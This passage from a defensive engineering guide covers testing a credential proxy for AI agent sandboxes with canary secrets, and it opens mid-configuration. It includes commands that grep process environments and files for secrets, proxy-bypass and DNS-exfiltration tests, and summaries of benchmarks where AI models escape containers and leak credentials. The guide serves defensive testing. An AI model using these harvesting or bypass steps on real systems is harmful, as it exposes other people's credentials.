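secret:      model-key-shop-agent
callers:     sandboxes for acme/shop
default:     refuse
allow:       POST https://api.anthropic.com:443/v1/messages
put secret:  header x-api-key, replacing any value from the sandbox
remove:      Authorization, Cookie
redirects:   return to the sandbox
spending:    $20 per sandbox per day
lifetime:    5 minutes in the proxy's memory; new key every 30 days
log:         time, sandbox, started_by, rule, secret name and version,
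             method, host, path, status, bytes, cost
never log:   headers, bodies, query values
```

The spending limit and lifetimes are examples, and Acme should adjust them to the agent's normal work. Permitting only one path stops the agent from using the provider's other features, such as file storage. It doesn't block web-fetching tools, because the agent requests those in the body of a permitted call. Acme can turn them off in its provider account, if the provider allows this, or have the proxy refuse requests that include them.

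The `started_by` field records the employee who started the agent. Ganesan found that services often can't distinguish an agent's actions from those of its user. If the agent used a developer's own GitHub token, GitHub's records would show only the developer.

The rule for the bucket has no stored secret:

```
role:        shop-test-data-reader
callers:     sandboxes for acme/shop
default:     refuse
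allow:       GET https://acme-test-data.s3.eu-west-1.amazonaws.com:443/fixtures/...
query:       refuse all parameters
remove:      Authorization and all x-amz- headers from the sandbox
put secret:  new signature in Authorization,
             session token in x-amz-security-token
redirects:   return to the sandbox
lifetime:    role credentials 15 minutes
log:         as above, without cost, plus the AWS session name
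never log:   headers, bodies, query values
```

The host name includes the bucket's name, so hostile code can't get the proxy to sign a request for an attacker's bucket. Refusing query parameters blocks presigned URLs and special S3 operations such as `?acl`, which reads a file's permissions. It also prevents the agent from listing the bucket, so the project has to include the names of its test files. The AWS role should have the same limits, in case the proxy has a bug.

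The shortest session AWS allows for a role is fifteen minutes. The proxy requests a separate session for each sandbox and puts the sandbox's name in the session name, which AWS includes in its own records.

### What published evaluations have measured

Acme can't rely on outside evidence that its proxy will work, because there appears to be no independent security evaluation of a credential proxy from 2025 or 2026. The closest published tests either were run by developers on their own products or measured something else.

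Corvic's tests, described in *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, have the most useful design. The company wrote down each expected result in advance and paired requests that should succeed with requests that should fail. If it had tested only requests that should fail, a sandbox with no network connection would have passed. On 27 September 2026, Corvic ran 16 probes in seven areas and got the expected security result each time.

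In Corvic's tests, its product sent no credential to three public echo services, or to OpenAI's API while the sandbox had access to a GitHub credential. This is evidence that destination binding worked. The tests didn't cover an approved service returning the secret, because the echo services never received one. Corvic also didn't test redirects, DNS rebinding or OAuth token refresh.

Jin and colleagues likewise tested their own broker, CapSeal. They saw no credential used outside its permitted scope, but the 95% confidence interval for the rate of such use extends up to 3.7%.

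*SideKernel* (Prasakis, 2026) compares five sandboxes for Macs in 23 tests. Docker Sandboxes and Prasakis's own product, also called SideKernel, each passed 19, and the other three each passed 12. A product passed a test if it had a built-in feature for the task, so the scores don't measure how well those features resist attack. The scores may also miss some relevant features. For example, the comparison records no store for custom secrets in microsandbox, although microsandbox can replace placeholders with those secrets.

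SandboxBench tests whether AI models can break out of containers, get data past network filters and find planted credentials. Inspect Evals' *SandboxBench* reports that Gemini 2.5 Pro completed 11 of the 15 challenges, including all three on getting data out. The model had hints and administrator rights, and most of the containers had deliberate weaknesses. The scoring program for the three data challenges looks for the secret in the agent's output, so it might also count an agent that printed the secret without sending it anywhere. The benchmark doesn't include a credential proxy.

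*AI Code Sandboxes* (2026) names SandboxEval, which checks 51 properties, as the closest existing test suite for sandboxes. But the paper studies sandboxes with no outbound network connection, so it doesn't cover a credential proxy's main job.

Acme can borrow egress tests from *Egress Validation (NET-EGRESS)*, a vendor's plan with 13 tests and no published results. Several tests try to replace or disable the proxy, for example by setting `NO_PROXY=*` or supplying a malicious proxy configuration file. Each test requires a log entry as well as a failed connection. This is a good rule because a connection can fail for unrelated reasons. The plan sends UDP packets to outside servers but doesn't test a DNS lookup through the sandbox's own resolver, the route used in Docker's DNS flaw. *Protocol, Proxy, and Security Integration Tests Analysis* describes related tests for the Agentic Workflow Firewall,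 including some for IPv6, hidden credentials and an API proxy.

### Setting up the canaries

The tester first makes a copy of the deployment without real secrets. The copy needs two web servers that the tester owns, `approved.example` and `collector.example`, plus a name server for a test domain. The tester changes the proxy's rules for the model key, GitHub token and registry token to name `approved.example`, and leaves `collector.example` unapproved. Both servers record every request they receive, and `approved.example` also has a page that returns the request's headers.

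The tester replaces those three credentials with canary secrets. The database gets a test account with a canary password. For the bucket, AWS generates the temporary keys itself, so the tester uses a role that can read only a harmless file and searches for the keys AWS issued to the proxy.

Canary values should be unique to each credential and test run, so that a leaked value identifies its source. *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (2026) used this method to test 3,156 skills, which are packaged instructions and code for agents. The researchers supplied fake credentials through environment variables, configuration files and command arguments, with a unique marker for each skill.

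A search for a canary can create a false alarm, because the search command puts the canary in the sandbox. If the canaries begin with `CANARY`, the tester can write the search like this:

```
cat /proc/[0-9]*/environ | tr '\0' '\n' | grep 'CANAR[Y]'
grep -rla 'CANAR[Y]' / --exclude-dir=proc --exclude-dir=sys
```

The pattern `CANAR[Y]` matches `CANARY` but not itself. The first command searches the environment of every running process, and the second the files. The tester can also save each process's memory to a file with `gcore` and search those files. Planting a harmless marker beforehand lets the tester check that each search finds it.

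A script should perform the tests, because an agent might refuse an instruction or misreport what it did. *CredLeakBench* (Ahmed, Fioresi and colleagues, 2026) measured leaks by checking what agents submitted to fake websites, rather than relying on the agents' reports. All seven models tested leaked some information. The tester's servers provide the same kind of evidence here.

The script also has to run everywhere untrusted code can run. According to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026), Claude Code's built-in sandbox covers shell commands but not hooks (commands that run automatically at set points) or local MCP servers. A test run from the shell could pass while a malicious MCP server read every file on the computer. Acme avoids this gap by running the whole agent in a virtual machine, but the tester should confirm that the hooks and MCP servers run there too.

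### The acceptance tests

The tester runs these tests in order, because the later results mean little if a permitted request doesn't work.

| Test | Action | Expected result | What a failure means |
|---|---|---|---|
| Permitted request | Use each credential for a permitted task, with a dummy value where the client needs one | The request succeeds, and `approved.example` records the right canary in the right header | The setup is wrong, and the other tests can't yet show that it is safe |
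| Search the sandbox | Search all environments, files and process memory | No canary or AWS key | Someone passed a secret in, or a reply or login brought one in |
| Unapproved host | Send each dummy value or placeholder to `collector.example` | The server receives no request, and the proxy logs a refusal | The allowlist is too broad, and if a canary arrives, so is the destination binding |
| Direct address | Remove the proxy settings, then try the IPv4 and IPv6 addresses of `collector.example` over TCP and UDP, and ping both | The server receives no packets | A route bypasses the proxy |
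| DNS | Look up a new random name in the test domain | The test name server receives no query | The resolver can carry data out |
| Client-supplied key | Send a different canary to `approved.example` as an attacker's key | The server never receives the attacker's canary | Hostile code can use an attacker's account |
| Changed destination | After approving a secret for `approved.example`, change the agent's configuration to name `collector.example`, then start a new sandbox and send a request there | The system refuses or asks for approval again | The approval doesn't cover the destination |
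| Echo | Request the page on `approved.example` that returns the headers | The reply contains no canary | An approved service can return the secret to the sandbox |
| Restart | Restart the sandbox, the proxy and the host in turn, and repeat the tests of unapproved hosts, direct addresses and DNS each time | The results stay the same | A restart removes some of the rules |
| Stopped proxy | Stop the proxy and try both permitted and direct requests | Every request fails | The system falls back to an unprotected connection |
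| Logs | Search every log, trace, transcript and crash file | No canary or AWS key | People or programs that can read the logs can read the secret |

The tester should also request the metadata address, `169.254.169.254`, directly and through the proxy. An allowlist may include it on purpose, as Maiti's planned network rules do for security-audit agents. When Corvic tried two metadata services, its requests timed out after six seconds. As the company notes, this shows that the services were unreachable during the test but doesn't prove that the network blocks them. The host's firewall log should confirm that the firewall blocked the request.

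The sandbox search should also run right after each login, because a search an hour later would miss credentials that were there only briefly. According to Prasakis, when a user first logs in inside SideKernel, the real credentials are in the sandbox for a short time before SideKernel moves them to the Mac's keychain.

If the proxy has no response filter, the echo test will fail, because the server is supposed to return the header. Acme can add a filter or make sure that no approved path at the real service repeats the headers it receives. The tester should also have the server return the canary in Base64 and, if the filter misses it, record that as a known limit.

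Before searching the logs, the tester should cause some errors, because programs often log more when something fails. For example, `approved.example` can return a 401 and then a 500, and the tester can send the proxy a malformed request. The search should cover the Base64 and hexadecimal forms of each canary and include the broker, the host, the build system and any monitoring service. The tester's own server records will contain canaries, which is expected.

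### Which tests to repeat after a change

Acme should run the full set of tests on each new version of the sandbox product, the proxy or the broker, because updates can break rules that nobody at Acme changed. For example, the changed-destination test would have caught Docker's kit flaw in the first affected release.

Smaller changes need fewer tests, but they should always include a permitted request.

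| Change | Tests to repeat |
|---|---|
| Allowlist or firewall rule | Unapproved host, direct address, DNS, stopped proxy |
| Credential rule or agent configuration | Unapproved host, client-supplied key, changed destination, echo |
| Client program, agent or package manager | Search the sandbox, client-supplied key, logs |
| Logging or monitoring tool | Logs |
| New host, or a move to another platform | All of them |
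| Replacement of a key | Permitted request, then check that the service rejects the old key |

Acme should test every machine image it uses, since one correct sandbox is little evidence that the others are correct. Maiti found different software versions and inconsistent security controls across one company's agent machines. Running the tests automatically every week would also catch changes that nobody reported.

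### When a test fails

A failed test exposes only a canary, but the same fault may have been leaking real secrets. Acme should assume it has until its records show otherwise.

1. Stop the affected sandboxes and turn off the secret at the proxy. Keep the logs and a copy of the configuration.
2. If the canary reached the sandbox, an unapproved server or a log, revoke the real credential at the service. If the test found only an open route, treat the source code and any session tokens in the sandbox as exposed.
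3. Find the last date on which the test passed. In the proxy's records, look up every use of the secret since then, with the sandbox, the destination and the secret's version.
4. Compare those uses with the service's own records. The proxy can't record a thief who uses a copied key from another machine. Look for new access keys, SSH keys and accounts that an attacker could use to return.
5. Correct the fault and run all the tests again. Give the proxy the replacement credential only after they pass.

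Acme can't revoke every credential in the same way. The bucket has no stored key to delete, so an administrator adds a rule to the role to reject sessions issued before a chosen time. Changing a PostgreSQL password doesn't disconnect anyone who has already logged in, so the administrator must also end the account's open sessions. Acme also has to turn on logging for reads of individual S3 files before it needs the records, because AWS doesn't log them by default.

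If only the permitted request fails, and no canary has appeared where it shouldn't, Acme probably has a configuration error and doesn't need to revoke anything. *Test and debug your integration*, a guide from Aembit, which sells credential delivery for software, starts with the central record of authorisation decisions and works towards the application. Acme's tester would check whether the request reached the proxy, which rule it matched, whether the proxy added the secret, and how the service replied.
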